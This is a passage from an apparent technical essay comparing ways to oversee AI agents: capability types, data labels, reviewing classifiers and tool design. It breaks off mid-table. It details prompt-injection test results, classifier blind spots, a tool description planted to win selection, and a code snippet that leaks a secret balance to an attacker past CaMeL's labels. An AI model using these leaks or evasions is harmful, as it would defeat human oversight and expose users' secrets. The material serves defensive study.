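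A sandbox can't easily prevent this kind of leak. An agent may have good reasons both to read a private file and to contact a model hosted elsewhere, and the leak happens when it passes data from one permitted operation to the other. Odersky and colleagues recommend using a sandbox as well, partly because the compiler has no control over external programs that the agent starts.

`Classified` protects against leaked secrets but not against mistaken deletions. TACIT's file handles include a `delete` function, so a correctly typed program with access to a backup directory can delete the last good backup. To prevent that, a developer would have to supply a narrower capability, which is much like supplying a narrow tool.

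### What the TACIT experiments found

Odersky and colleagues tested secrecy on a software project with a directory of keys and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 hidden instructions, which gave 120 trials, and added 11 tasks in which the user asked for the secrets directly or under a pretext. Each model did all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text.

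| | Trials without a leak, secrets wrapped | Trials without a leak, plain text | Ordinary tasks completed, secrets wrapped | Ordinary tasks completed, plain text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Sonnet resisted all 120 hidden instructions even without the wrapper, so those trials provide little evidence about the types. MiniMax provides the clearest evidence. It gave up secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious tasks when the secrets were plain text, and in none when they were wrapped. Sonnet's lower completion rate with plain text may be an artefact, because the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

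Writing Scala did little to hurt the agents' performance. On the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, MiniMax's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7% with TACIT. In the customer-service tests, the compiler rejected at most 8% of the programs, and the agent usually fixed them in one or two attempts.

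### LACUNA and the variables in scope

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) builds on the same compiler and shares several authors with TACIT. A developer leaves a gap in a program by writing `agent[T](task)`, where `T` is the type of result the program needs. When the running program reaches the gap, the model receives the task, the type and the variables available at that point, and writes code to fill the gap. The compiler checks this code as if the developer had written it there.

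The variables in scope therefore serve as the agent's permissions. A developer could put one gap where the agent's code can reach only a read-only list of backups, and another where it can reach a function that deletes them. An instruction hidden in the list could not make the code in the first gap delete anything, because no variable in scope there allows deletion. This protection requires capture checking, which is optional in LACUNA, and safe mode, which blocks reflection and stops the code from launching other programs.

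The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of code as a whole. In one of the paper's examples, the model writes code that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the code, so the balance remains 100. In an untyped language, the subtraction might have happened before the error appeared. This protects only against errors the compiler can find, so a program that compiles and then fails at its fifth deletion will already have deleted four backups.

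LACUNA passed about 400 tests of whether the compiler accepts good code and rejects bad code, but it did worse than ordinary tool calls on real tasks. On 392 tasks from τ²-bench, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with tool calls. The gap was 14 points overall and 22 points on the retail tasks, though Zhao and colleagues describe the results as on par. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, a weaker model, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with tool calls, and the compiler rejected 89% of the programs Gemini wrote for the telecom tasks. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models have seen too little Scala in training. That can't be the whole explanation, because models using TACIT also have to write Scala and performed no worse on the same benchmark, though TACIT was tested with other models and on only two of the four domains.

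### CaMeL and permissions on data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, attaches permissions to data instead of code. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain its design through an example in which a user wants to send Bob a message, and Bob's address is somewhere in a chat channel:

1. A privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python: read the channel, extract Bob's address, send the message.
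2. An interpreter runs the plan. It passes the channel's messages to a second model, which has no tools and can only return a value, here an address.
3. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it. It labels the address as coming from the channel, where anyone could have written it.
4. Before each tool call, a policy examines the arguments and their labels. A policy that allows messages only to trusted recipients would refuse this call.

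A malicious message in the channel can't add steps to the plan, because the privileged model never reads it. It can still change the address, which the labels are meant to catch. But the policy also blocks the call when the address is genuine, so CaMeL can prevent useful work.

Zhao and colleagues compared LACUNA with the published results for CaMeL and TACIT on AgentDojo, the same collection of simulated tasks that Progent's developers used. The table gives the share of tasks completed and how many of the roughly 950 attacks on each system and model succeeded.

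| | CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|
| **o4-mini-high:** banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 66.0% |
| Office work | 81.4% | 52.9% | 55.5% |
| Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 49.5% |
| Travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 71.4% |
| Successful attacks | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| **Gemini 2.5 Pro:** banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 63.2% |
| Office work | 53.8% | 50.5% | 56.3% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 42.9% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 63.6% |
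| Successful attacks | 0 | 0 | 7 |

All three stopped nearly every attack. Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's completion rates comparable to CaMeL's, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT's were more than 20 points lower on office work and Slack. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that the compiler can't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability its task requires, which is consistent with LACUNA's seven failures with Gemini.

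### Later findings about CaMeL

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with two newer models. With its policies off, the agent completed 67% and 71% of the tasks. With them on, it completed 37.5% with either model and blocked every attack in the runs that finished. The researchers have a competing system, and 16 tasks is a small sample, but another team found a similar drop with its own system, TypeGuard, which enforces comparable policies in the language Haskell. TypeGuard completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on.

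Tests with new attacks gave similar results. In *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), CaMeL reduced the attack success rate from 17.5% to 2.5%, the lowest of the defences tested, but completed only 27.5% of the tasks. Another defence, PromptArmor, let through 7.5% of the attacks and completed 90% of the tasks.

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that this loss will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. Better planning would help with tasks that fail because the plan is wrong, but it would help less with the losses that Garby and colleagues measured, since the same models did much better with the policies off. Their own system lets the privileged model mark in advance which untrusted data an action may use. With GPT-5.2, it completed 75% of the banking tasks. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user told the agent to pay whatever a file said,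 and an attacker had replaced the file. The system didn't stop these attacks because labels can't distinguish a real bill from a fake one when both come from the same file.

Garby and colleagues also found ways to get secrets past CaMeL's labels. One uses a program like this, in which `balance` is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich")
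```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and the fourth line does nothing. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when a line that depends on a secret changes it, so `rich` remains public and the email goes out. The attacker learns that the balance is high. In TACIT, wrapping the balance would block this program, because code can examine a wrapped balance only inside a pure function, which can't change a variable outside itself. TACIT doesn't prevent timing leaks, however.

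### Can a checker list the effects in advance?

The main objection to all four systems is that an overseer has to read programs. An approver who could judge `delete_backup(id="b-1042")` at a glance now has to follow a loop and work out which values `b.id` will take. A short program like the one for backups may be easier to judge than forty prompts, but a longer one with branches that depend on earlier results can be as hard to follow as a shell script.

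Defenders can reply that the overseer doesn't have to read the program if a checker can list its possible effects before it runs. The systems differ in how much of this checking they allow.

| | What limits the program | Can a checker list its effects before it runs? |
|---|---|---|
| Code Mode | The functions the developer supplies | No. The runtime records each call when the program makes it |
| TACIT | The capture sets in its types | Yes, as a list of capabilities |
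| LACUNA | The variables in scope | Yes, with capture checking on, but only as an upper limit where the code contains further gaps |
| CaMeL | Labels on data and a policy for each call | Not by itself. CaMeLoT adds a check of the plan |

With Code Mode, an overseer knows in advance only which functions are available, and that list is the same for every program. The overseer could scan the code for function names, but the scan would miss any request path that the program builds while it runs.

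TACIT's compiler does produce a list, but how informative it is depends on the library. If the developer supplies one capability for a document store and another for a single output file, the capture sets will distinguish them. But code that calls `requestFileSystem` needs a general input/output capability, so the list for a whole program may contain only that. TACIT uses the sets to accept or reject code, and a developer who wanted to show them to an approver would have to build the display.

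In LACUNA, the model's code can also contain new gaps that the model fills later, and nobody can list the exact effects of that later code before it exists. The compiler can still guarantee that the later code will use only the capabilities in scope at its gap, but the earlier code may already have acted by the time the compiler checks the later code.

CaMeL's plan is complete before any tool runs, which makes it the easiest of the four to examine in advance. CaMeLoT, by Nikolaou and colleagues, translates the plan into a diagram of its possible steps and uses a standard verification program to check every path through it. It can check rules about the order of calls, such as requiring approval before the agent disconnects a computer from the network. CaMeL's own policies each apply to a single call and can't easily express such rules. CaMeLoT reproduced 22 of the 28 policies from CaMeL's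 AgentDojo tests. Most of the others depend on facts that nobody knows until the plan runs, such as who can read a shared file at that point. Because CaMeLoT allows for any number of passes through a loop, it may reject some safe plans.

For the backup program, any of these checkers could report at most that the program lists backups and may delete them. It couldn't report which ones, because the identifiers come from the list, so the overseer would be as unsure of the targets as with `delete_backups(filter: string)`. A developer could split the task in two. A program with access only to `list_backups` would return the forty identifiers, and a second call would then contain them as plain values, which the overseer could read before anything was deleted.

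## The case for a model that reviews each command

Splitting the backup task in two gives an overseer forty plain identifiers to read, but a developer has to design the task that way. Supporters of a reviewing model think overseers need better review of commands more than they need narrower tools. They would keep the shell and the other broad tools, and have a second model read each command before it runs and compare it with what the user asked for.

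Claude Code's auto mode is probably the best-documented system of this kind. Anthropic described its design in March 2026, and new terminal sessions now start in auto mode on every plan.

### Rules that match the text of a command

An older way to avoid approval prompts is to write allow-rules. In Claude Code, `Bash(npm test)` lets the agent run that one command without asking, and `Bash(python:*)` lets it run any command that begins with `python`. The harness only compares text, so applying a rule takes almost no compute and the same command always gets the same result.

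Narrow rules take a lot of upkeep, because agents rarely phrase a command the same way twice. In Vorwerck's *Running auto mode in production* (2026), an engineering manager at Garner Health describes a tedious cycle of curating lists of approved commands and watching the harness reject commands that the agent had joined together. Many users write broader rules instead. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that, as of June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written an allow-rule for the shell. 5% allowed any command, and another 43% had rules for whole interpreters, such as Python or Node. The share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

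A Python program can delete files, contact servers and start other programs, so a rule that allows the whole interpreter permits nearly everything the account can do. Anthropic doesn't specify whether the 5% and 43% are shares of all active users or only of those who had written a rule. In the first case, almost everyone who wrote a rule wrote one that limits very little, and in the second, about half did.

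OpenAI found the same habit among its own staff. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that a sizable minority of internal users allowed every command beginning with `python`. One user had a standing rule that let Codex start a second copy of itself with its restrictions off.

These figures are counts of rules, not accidents, but they suggest that text rules on a shell tend to widen until an overseer can learn little from them. A rule for a narrow tool can't widen in this way, because a rule that allows `delete_backup` covers only the deletion of backups, however carelessly the user approved it.

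### How auto mode sorts actions

When a session enters auto mode, the harness sets aside rules that would let the agent run arbitrary code, and restores them when the session leaves the mode. Narrow rules such as `Bash(npm test)` stay in force, as do rules that forbid something. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the remaining actions fall into three tiers:

1. Tools that cannot change anything, such as those for reading and searching files, run at once.
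2. Tools that write or edit files inside the project directory also run at once, because version control lets the user see and reverse the changes.
3. Everything else goes to a classifier, a model that decides whether to allow or block the action. This tier includes shell commands, web requests, calls to outside services, and file changes elsewhere on the machine.

An agent with the backup task could therefore read a list of backups and edit a cleanup script in the project without review, but the classifier would examine the command that runs the script.

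The classifier works in two stages. A fast stage answers yes or no in a single token, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags an action, the model receives the same input again and reasons about it at length before deciding. Most actions pass the fast stage, so only a few need the longer reasoning.

A blocked agent receives the reason and can look for a safer way to do the task. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, the harness goes back to asking the user.

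### What the classifier receives

In the March design, the classifier received the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, including the text of commands. The harness removed the agent's explanations because an agent might mislead the classifier by writing that a deletion is safe or that the user has already agreed to it.

The harness also removed tool results, such as the contents of files and web pages, because hidden instructions usually reach an agent through them. The agent still read these results, so a separate check scanned them first and added a warning to anything suspicious.

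In Anthropic's tests, the classifier did worse on a set of real overreaching actions when it also received the agent's explanations and the tool results. A version that received only tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked things that users had plainly requested.

Without tool results, the classifier can't always tell where an identifier came from. If the agent tries to cancel job `abc123` and the user never mentioned that job, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found the identifier in a list or made it up. The classifier can examine a script that the agent wrote during the session, because the text was part of an earlier tool call. But a script that was already in the project would enter the session only as a tool result, so the classifier would presumably have to judge the command that runs it without seeing the script.

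The classifier can sometimes make a good decision despite missing facts. Anthropic designed auto mode to block cases such as an agent that hits a login error and starts searching configuration files for other tokens, much as the PocketOS agent did. Even without knowing whether the volume belonged to staging or production, a reviewer could notice that nobody had authorised the agent to use that token or delete that volume.

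According to Anthropic's current documentation on permission modes, the classifier now also receives the project's standing instructions. Before a command that could discard uncommitted work, the harness checks whether any such work exists and passes the result to the classifier.

Some rules now make the agent write clearer commands. By default, the classifier blocks `rm -rf "$BACKUP_DIR"`, which deletes a directory and everything in it, if nothing in the classifier's input shows the variable's value. The agent can try again with the actual path in the command. An approver or log reader can then see which directory the command targets, as they could with a narrow tool, even though the agent is still using the same shell.

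### The March 2026 error rates

Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of actions. The ordinary calls came from its employees' work, and the overreaching actions came from real sessions in which an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterwards.

| Test set | Measure | Fast stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 ordinary tool calls | Harmless calls that the classifier blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
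| 52 real overreaching actions | Actions that it missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic data leaks | Leaks that it missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage cuts blocked ordinary calls from about 850 to 40, but it also lets through some dangerous actions that the fast stage had caught. The 17% miss rate represents about nine misses in a small sample, so its 95% confidence interval runs from roughly 9% to 30%.

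In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified what the command would do but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission. For example, it identified a force-push, which overwrites the history of a shared project, but treated "clean up the PR" as permission for it. A user who says this is asking for a tidier set of proposed changes and may not have thought about the project's history. In other cases, the classifier treated the user's approval of an earlier, similar action as covering the new one.

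This is good evidence that narrower tools are not the main need. A call such as `force_push(branch="main")` would have given the classifier no new information about the effect, which it had already identified. The evidence comes from only a handful of misses, though, and a narrow tool can help with authorization in another way. A policy for one task, like those in Progent, sets the allowed branch or recipient before the agent proposes a call.

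Anthropic reports that it tried to fix the problem by rewording the classifier's instructions but found no change whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks. The current documentation asks users to be specific. Saying "You can force-push" does not lift the block, because the user also has to name the branch, and the approval normally covers one action. Users can also forbid actions in conversation, but the classifier may lose that limit when the harness shortens a long session, so a written deny rule is safer.

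### Newer results

In August 2026, Anthropic reported that auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands in a controlled test, far more than paid testers blocked when they saw the same commands. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, tested auto mode's classifier on synthetic attacks before and after Anthropic strengthened it. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7%, and the classifier also improved on attacks that Anthropic had never seen. The main change was that Anthropic gave the classifier more facts, such as whether a repository is public. This fits the earlier suggestion that overseers lack information more often than they face undecidable programs.

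Anthropic also examined real sessions its safety systems had flagged in May and June. Serious harm the user had not explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

Auto mode did worse when outside researchers tested it on harder requests. For *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) wrote 128 requests in which the user's aim was clear but the permitted scope or risk was not. The agent took 253 actions that changed something, and auto mode as a whole missed 81.0% of those that went too far. The classifier reviewed 160 of the 253 actions. It missed 70.3% of the overreaching actions it reviewed and blocked 31.9% of the acceptable ones. Ji and colleagues attribute the difference from Anthropic's 17% miss rate to the different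 workload. Their requests concentrate on unclear authorization, which Anthropic had already identified as the classifier's weak point.

Sharma, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *Ajar*, measured how much a defence would allow beyond what a task needed, whether or not an agent tried it. They used the 97 ordinary tasks in AgentDojo, whose tools are typed. For each task, they tested the defence on a range of unnecessary calls and weighted each call by its possible harm, from 1 for a harmless read to 27 for an irreversible payment to someone else. The results below are for Claude Sonnet 5 as the deciding model. Permission Assistant, like auto mode, has a model judge each call.

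| | Unneeded calls allowed, weighted by harm | Legitimate calls refused | Change in tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Auto mode | 30% | 1.3–2.5% | −3.4 points |
| Permission Assistant | 8% | 5.4% | −11.3 points |
| Progent | 10% | 13.3% | None |
| CaMeL | 9% | 32.3% | −21.6 points |

Auto mode was only slightly stricter than a simple list of the tools each task needs, which allowed 36% with no limit on the tools' arguments. The comparison is somewhat unfair to auto mode, because Sharma and colleagues scored it on a smaller set of calls and without the session history. Auto mode also aims to block dangerous actions, not every unnecessary one. Permission Assistant's result shows that a reviewing model can be much stricter, though the agent then completes fewer tasks. Progent allowed a third as much as auto mode without reducing the number of completed tasks, but only because the tools had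 separate arguments that its rules could limit.

### Where narrow tools save review

The first two tiers of auto mode depend on narrow tools. The harness can let a file search through without review because the search tool can't change anything. It can let an edit through because the edit tool takes a path, which the harness can compare with the project directory. If the agent made the same edit with a shell command, the harness would have to determine from the command's text which files would change.

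Let *r* be the share of actions that reach the classifier, *f* the share of those that the fast stage flags, and *c*₁ and *c*₂ the costs of the two stages. The average cost of review per action is then

*r* × (*c*₁ + *f* × *c*₂).

The two-stage design keeps *f* low, while narrow tools keep *r* low. According to Anthropic's documentation, the added cost and delay come mainly from shell commands and network operations. In a harness like Schmid's, where the agent does nearly everything through Bash, *r* would be close to 1 unless the harness could recognise harmless commands. Claude Code has a built-in set of read-only shell commands for some purposes, so it in effect treats a few uses of the shell as narrow tools.

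But a tool's type is only a rough guide to how dangerous an action is. In the tests by Ji and colleagues, 36.8% of the actions that changed something were edits inside the project, which the classifier never examined. The problem was worst in cleanup tasks, where auto mode missed 92.9% of the overreaching actions. When the expected command was unavailable, agents often edited the files that recorded a system's state. Each edit was a clear call to a narrow tool, and version control may well have shown the change to the text, but it would not have undone whatever another program did after reading the file.

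Anthropic's current rules close part of this gap by checking some changes later. If the agent edits a deployment script to send secrets elsewhere, the classifier is supposed to block the change when the agent commits or pushes it. Edits to certain protected files go to the classifier immediately.

When Claude Code's own Code Mode is on, the classifier reviews the agent's code once, before it runs, and does not review the tool calls inside it. It would therefore review the backup program once instead of at every deletion, but it would not see which backups the loop would delete.

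### Review at the sandbox boundary in Codex

According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the Codex agent works inside a sandbox and asks for approval when it needs to go outside, for example to reach a blocked website or change a file elsewhere. By default, the request goes to the user. In the review mode, it goes to a second agent, which approves or denies it and gives a reason. This mode doesn't change the sandbox's limits.

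A command that stays inside the sandbox needs no review, however obscure its text. Trębacz and colleagues give an illustrative snapshot of use at OpenAI in which 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied 7. The agent found a safer way to continue after 4 of those denials and stopped to ask the user after the other 3.

Developers can therefore keep *r* low without narrow tools if the agent can do most of its work in a sandbox. This works well for coding, where the agent can do much of the work on a copy of the project. It helps less with an agent whose job is to delete backups at a cloud provider, because every useful action affects something outside the sandbox. For calls to MCP servers and connected apps, Codex also relies partly on the tools' labels to decide what needs approval, so tool design still matters for those calls.

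The reviewer in Codex receives the agent's visible updates and relevant tool results but, like Claude Code's classifier, does not receive the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also make its own read-only checks. It could therefore trace where job `abc123` came from, but it would have to read text that an attacker may have written.

The reviewer approved 99.1% of a sample of real requests that users had approved. It caught 90.3% of synthetic overreaching actions and 99.3% of synthetic prompt injections that involved running outside code, stealing secrets or uploading data. The catch rate for injections falls to 90.2% when the tests include deletion and tampering, though Trębacz and colleagues consider many of the missed actions too minor to block. Because OpenAI and Anthropic used different tests, these rates can't show which company's choice of input is better.

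A direct comparison that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs doesn't settle the matter either. No prompt injections succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol with Codex's reviewer. But the newest Claude models resisted almost all the attacks even without auto mode, so the difference comes mostly from the agents themselves. With both the sandbox and the reviewer off, 19.03% of attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol, which suggests the two together helped considerably.

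Trębacz and colleagues warn that testers sometimes misled the reviewer into approving commands, and that the reviewer offers little protection against a model that deliberately hides its intentions. Such a model could make a harmful request look ordinary or do damage inside the sandbox. OpenAI advises against broad text rules, such as one that allows all `python` commands, because they let the agent cross the boundary without review.

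### Fixed limits around the reviewer

Both companies supplement the reviewer with controls that don't depend on a model's judgement. Internally, OpenAI requires Codex to run in the sandbox and limits which websites it can reach. Anthropic recommends that people still review high-stakes changes to production systems.

The customers that Vorwerck interviewed for Anthropic's website work in a similar way. Engineers at Nuro, which develops self-driving technology, use their settings to forbid the most dangerous commands, such as recursive deletes. Gusto, a business software company, sends its agents' MCP traffic through a proxy that restricts the tools before auto mode reviews anything. One of Gusto's cloud engineers uses auto mode for most work but switches it off for production infrastructure and checks each tool call there by hand.

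## What many narrow tools cost in tokens, money and task success

Narrow tools leave a reviewer with fewer actions to check, but several teams that built large sets of them decided the drawbacks were too great. The objection is that tool descriptions fill the model's context, a long list of tools makes wrong choices more likely, a series of small operations takes more steps than one program, and somebody has to write and maintain every tool.

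### The size of tool descriptions

A model keeps nothing between requests, so the harness normally resends the tool descriptions with each request. Models read text as tokens, which are short pieces of text, not the API tokens that give access to an account. The context window is the largest number of tokens a model can take in at once.

Cloudflare reports that turning its API's 2,594 operations into separate tools with full descriptions would take about 1,170,000 tokens, more than most models' context windows can hold. Descriptions that cover only the required parameters would take about 244,000. The two tools in Cloudflare's Code Mode server take about 1,000.

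If an agent has *n* tools and the average description is *d* tokens long, the descriptions take up *n* × *d* tokens. Cloudflare's figures give

*d* = 1,170,000 / 2,594 ≈ 451 tokens with full descriptions, and

*d* = 244,000 / 2,594 ≈ 94 tokens with required parameters only.

The table applies these averages to agents of different sizes, with a context window of 200,000 tokens.

| Tools | Full descriptions | Share of window | Required parameters only | Share of window |
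|---|---|---|---|---|
| 4 | 1,800 | 0.9% | 380 | 0.2% |
| 20 | 9,000 | 4.5% | 1,900 | 0.9% |
| 100 | 45,100 | 23% | 9,400 | 4.7% |
| 500 | 225,500 | 113% | 47,000 | 24% |

The objection to narrow tools is weak when an agent has only about 20 of them, as many useful agents do. For example, the agent for Microsoft's Dynamics 365 business software in *Less Context, Better Agents* (2026) has 21. The objection is hard to answer for an agent with several hundred tools, unless the harness leaves out some of the tool descriptions.

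The average number of tokens per tool varies a good deal between sets of tools. The 374 tools in *Cartograph* (2026) take 38,250 tokens, or about 102 each. *Scalable LLM Agent Tool Access in the Cloud* (2026) reports that 120 tools for managing cloud networks take at least 56,000 tokens with some models and over 166,000 with others, or roughly 470 to 1,400 each. At 1,400 tokens each, twenty tools would fill 14% of the context window.

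Providers reduce the cost in money by storing, or caching, the repeated beginning of a request and charging less to read it again. According to *Fewer Tokens, Better Action* (2026), a study of robot control, OpenAI's September 2026 price for GPT-6 Astra was $10 per million input tokens, $12.50 to write them to the cache and $1 to read them from it. Sending 9,000 tokens of tool descriptions in each of 20 requests would cost $1.80 without caching and about 28 cents with it.

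Tool descriptions take up the same space in the context even when caching makes them cheaper. *Hybrid Semantic Tool Discovery for Enterprise MCP Gateway* (2026) gives the example of PayPal, whose tool descriptions total 140,200 tokens. They would fill 70% of a 200,000-token window before the user asks anything.

### Loading descriptions on demand

The usual reply to the context objection is tool search, in which the model sees a description only when it needs the tool:

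1. The harness stores all the descriptions outside the model's context. It sends the model a search tool and perhaps a few tools that most tasks need.
2. The model searches for what it wants to do, for example "delete a backup".
3. The harness returns the full descriptions of the closest matches.
4. The model calls one of them.

*Harness Engineering* (2026), a study of the source code of eleven coding agents, describes several versions of tool search. Claude Code has 43 tools but loads only a core set at the start. Codex ranks the tools it hasn't loaded by how well their descriptions match the search terms. Hermes switches to search when descriptions from MCP servers and plug-ins would fill more than 10% of the context window. With a 200,000-token window and Cloudflare's average description lengths, an agent would reach that limit at about 44 tools with full descriptions, or about 213 with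 short ones.

The savings can be large. In *Cartograph*, the permanent tools take 169 tokens and a search that returns five tools adds about 306, compared with 38,250 for the whole set. Agents also don't need to search before every action. *Tool Recommendation for Multi-Step Agents* (2026) reports about one search for every eight tool calls (0.12 per call) over 30 days of real use.

Alier Forment, Casañ Guerrero and colleagues (2026), in *The Scaffolding Matters More Than the Interface*, ran the same GitHub task in seven harnesses. Four of them sent all 44 tool descriptions from GitHub's MCP server with every request, and their median completed run used about 217,000 input tokens. Hermes sent seven descriptions and fetched the others when the model requested them, and its median run used about 71,000. This suggests that fetching descriptions on request saves tokens, but Hermes was the only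 harness tested that worked this way, and it differed from the others in many other respects.

Tool search preserves most of what an overseer gains from narrow tools, because the eventual call still specifies one operation and its arguments. However, the harness must apply its permission rules to the name of the underlying tool. In Hermes, the model calls the tools it finds through a general tool named `tool_call`, so a rule that checked only that name would treat a search and a deletion alike.

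Search can also miss tools. In *Beyond Plain MCP*, Rai (2026) tested a small model that chose tools from a shortlist before the main agent started work. The shortlist contained every tool the task needed 65% of the time when the catalogue had 200 tools, and 44% of the time when it had 2,000. An agent that can search again during the task does better. In Rai's small test with 2,000 tools, such an agent completed nine of ten tasks by writing code that called the tools it found. Carey adds that somebody has to maintain and evaluate the search function.

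A dishonest supplier could also write a tool description designed to come up in searches. When Rai added a malicious tool whose description included an instruction to always select it, a general language model chose it in all 39 tasks, and a model trained to score each tool separately chose it in 62% of them. An overseer should therefore not assume that a tool is permitted because it was selected.

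### Wrong choices among many tools

GitHub found that its assistant Copilot did worse with its full set of about 40 built-in tools than with a smaller one. The agent ignored explicit instructions, used tools incorrectly and made unnecessary calls. GitHub reduced the default set to 13 tools and put the rest into four groups that the model can open when needed. On two sets of programming tasks, with GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, the success rate rose by 2 to 5 percentage points. In a comparison among real users, responses finished 400 milliseconds sooner on average.

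The model could still open the wrong group, and each mistake required an extra request. GitHub therefore added a step that compares the user's query with every tool's description and loads the likely tools in advance. In tests, the tool the model needed was already visible 94.5% of the time, compared with 87.5% when a language model chose the tools and 69.0% with a fixed list.

GitHub kept the tools that agents used most and hid specialised ones, such as those for data-science notebooks. The 13 remaining tools still include separate ones for reading, editing and searching files, as well as a terminal. The case therefore supports showing fewer tools at a time, as tool search does, although people sometimes cite it as evidence against narrow tools.

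*Scalable LLM Agent Tool Access in the Cloud* reports that models chose unsuitable tools and produced badly formed calls more often as tool descriptions filled more of the context. The share of requests in which the model called no tool rose from 8% to 19%. With 120 tools, one model took more than 100 seconds to choose a tool and write its arguments.

### Extra steps

Each request to the model also includes the conversation so far, so the number of steps can matter more than the number of tools. If the first request is *q* tokens long and each step adds *h* tokens, then *T* requests send a total of

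*T* × *q* + *h* × *T*(*T* − 1) / 2

input tokens. Suppose an agent deletes forty backups with `preview_delete` and `commit_delete`, which takes eighty calls. If *q* is 5,000 and *h* is 200, it sends about 1,030,000 tokens. The descriptions of four tools would account for only about 144,000 of them. Most of the total would qualify for the cheap cached rate, but the user would still have to wait for eighty replies. Versions of the two tools that accept lists of identifiers would avoid most of this cost, as would a harness that lets the model make several calls in one reply.

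The best size for a tool also changes during a task. *CIPO* (2026) compared single tools with stored procedures that combine several tools, at many points during agents' tasks. The procedures did better at 37% of those points and the single tools at 21%, with little difference at the rest.

The most detailed evidence on steps comes from Xu, Saghir and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil Is in the Interface*. They compared six sets of tools for repairing faults in software projects:

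- a shell only;
- a shell with four narrow tools for searching, viewing, editing and creating files;
- a shell with a tool that searches the project from a plain-language question;
- a shell with a tool for recording hypotheses;
- a shell with a scratchpad for notes;
- Python only, with the agent writing a block of code for each action.

Three models attempted each of 65 problems ten times with each of the six sets, for a total of 11,700 runs. All six sets gave the agent roughly the same powers, and each model solved a similar share of the problems with every set.

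Xu and colleagues also measured consistency, because a user may care whether an agent succeeds every time. If an agent solves a problem in *c* of *n* attempts, the measure for groups of *k* attempts is

pass^*k* = C(*c*, *k*) / C(*n*, *k*),

where C(*n*, *k*) is the number of ways to choose *k* attempts from *n*. This is the share of such groups in which every attempt succeeded. An agent that solves a problem in nine of ten attempts scores 0.5 for *k* = 5 and only 0.1 for *k* = 9.

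The table shows what happened when Xu and colleagues added the four narrow file tools to the shell.

| | Qwen3-Coder-30B | Kimi K2.5 | Claude Sonnet 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Consistency over nine attempts | 0.020 → 0.094 | 0.266 → 0.280 | 0.252 → 0.283 |
| Steps per run | 64 → 43 | 56 → 59 | 74 → 80 |
| Input tokens per run | 980,000 → 662,000 | 950,000 → 1,141,000 | 2,140,000 → 2,576,000 |

This was the only change that made all three models more consistent. Qwen, the weakest model, gained by far the most, though it started from a very low level. With the shell alone, it averaged 1.64 program-breaking edits and 0.96 badly formed commands per run. With the narrow tools, those averages fell to 0.19 and 0.01. Qwen named wrong files or other wrong targets more often with the narrow tools, perhaps because these tools reject mistakes that a shell command accepts.

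The two stronger models made small gains with the narrow tools but used about 20% more input tokens. They had been combining several operations in one shell command, and the narrow tools split this work into separate steps. Qwen rarely combined operations, so it had less efficiency to lose. Current models are stronger than any of these three, so they will probably gain less consistency from narrow file tools and lose more efficiency.

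Python had the opposite effect, reducing the number of steps by 28% to 40%, depending on the model, with little change in the share of problems solved. It did not improve consistency, and it made Qwen less consistent. With the search tool, agents read more of the relevant files but also more irrelevant ones. The hypothesis tool and scratchpad made little difference.

### A single code tool compared with a full set

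Yang, Yu and Desell (2026), in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, took the comparison further by removing an agent's usual tools altogether. They tested three sets:

- the agent's default tools, including a shell and tools for editing files;
- a shell with tools for reading and searching, but none for editing;
- one tool, `execute_code`, which runs Python and shell code and remembers variables between calls.

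Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Codex with GPT-5.5 each used every tool set. The agents attempted 93 computation tasks, such as processing data, and 100 tasks that required changing existing software, three times each. The table compares `execute_code` with the cheaper of the other two sets.

| Tasks | Agent | Change in pass rate | Change in cost |
|---|---|---|---|
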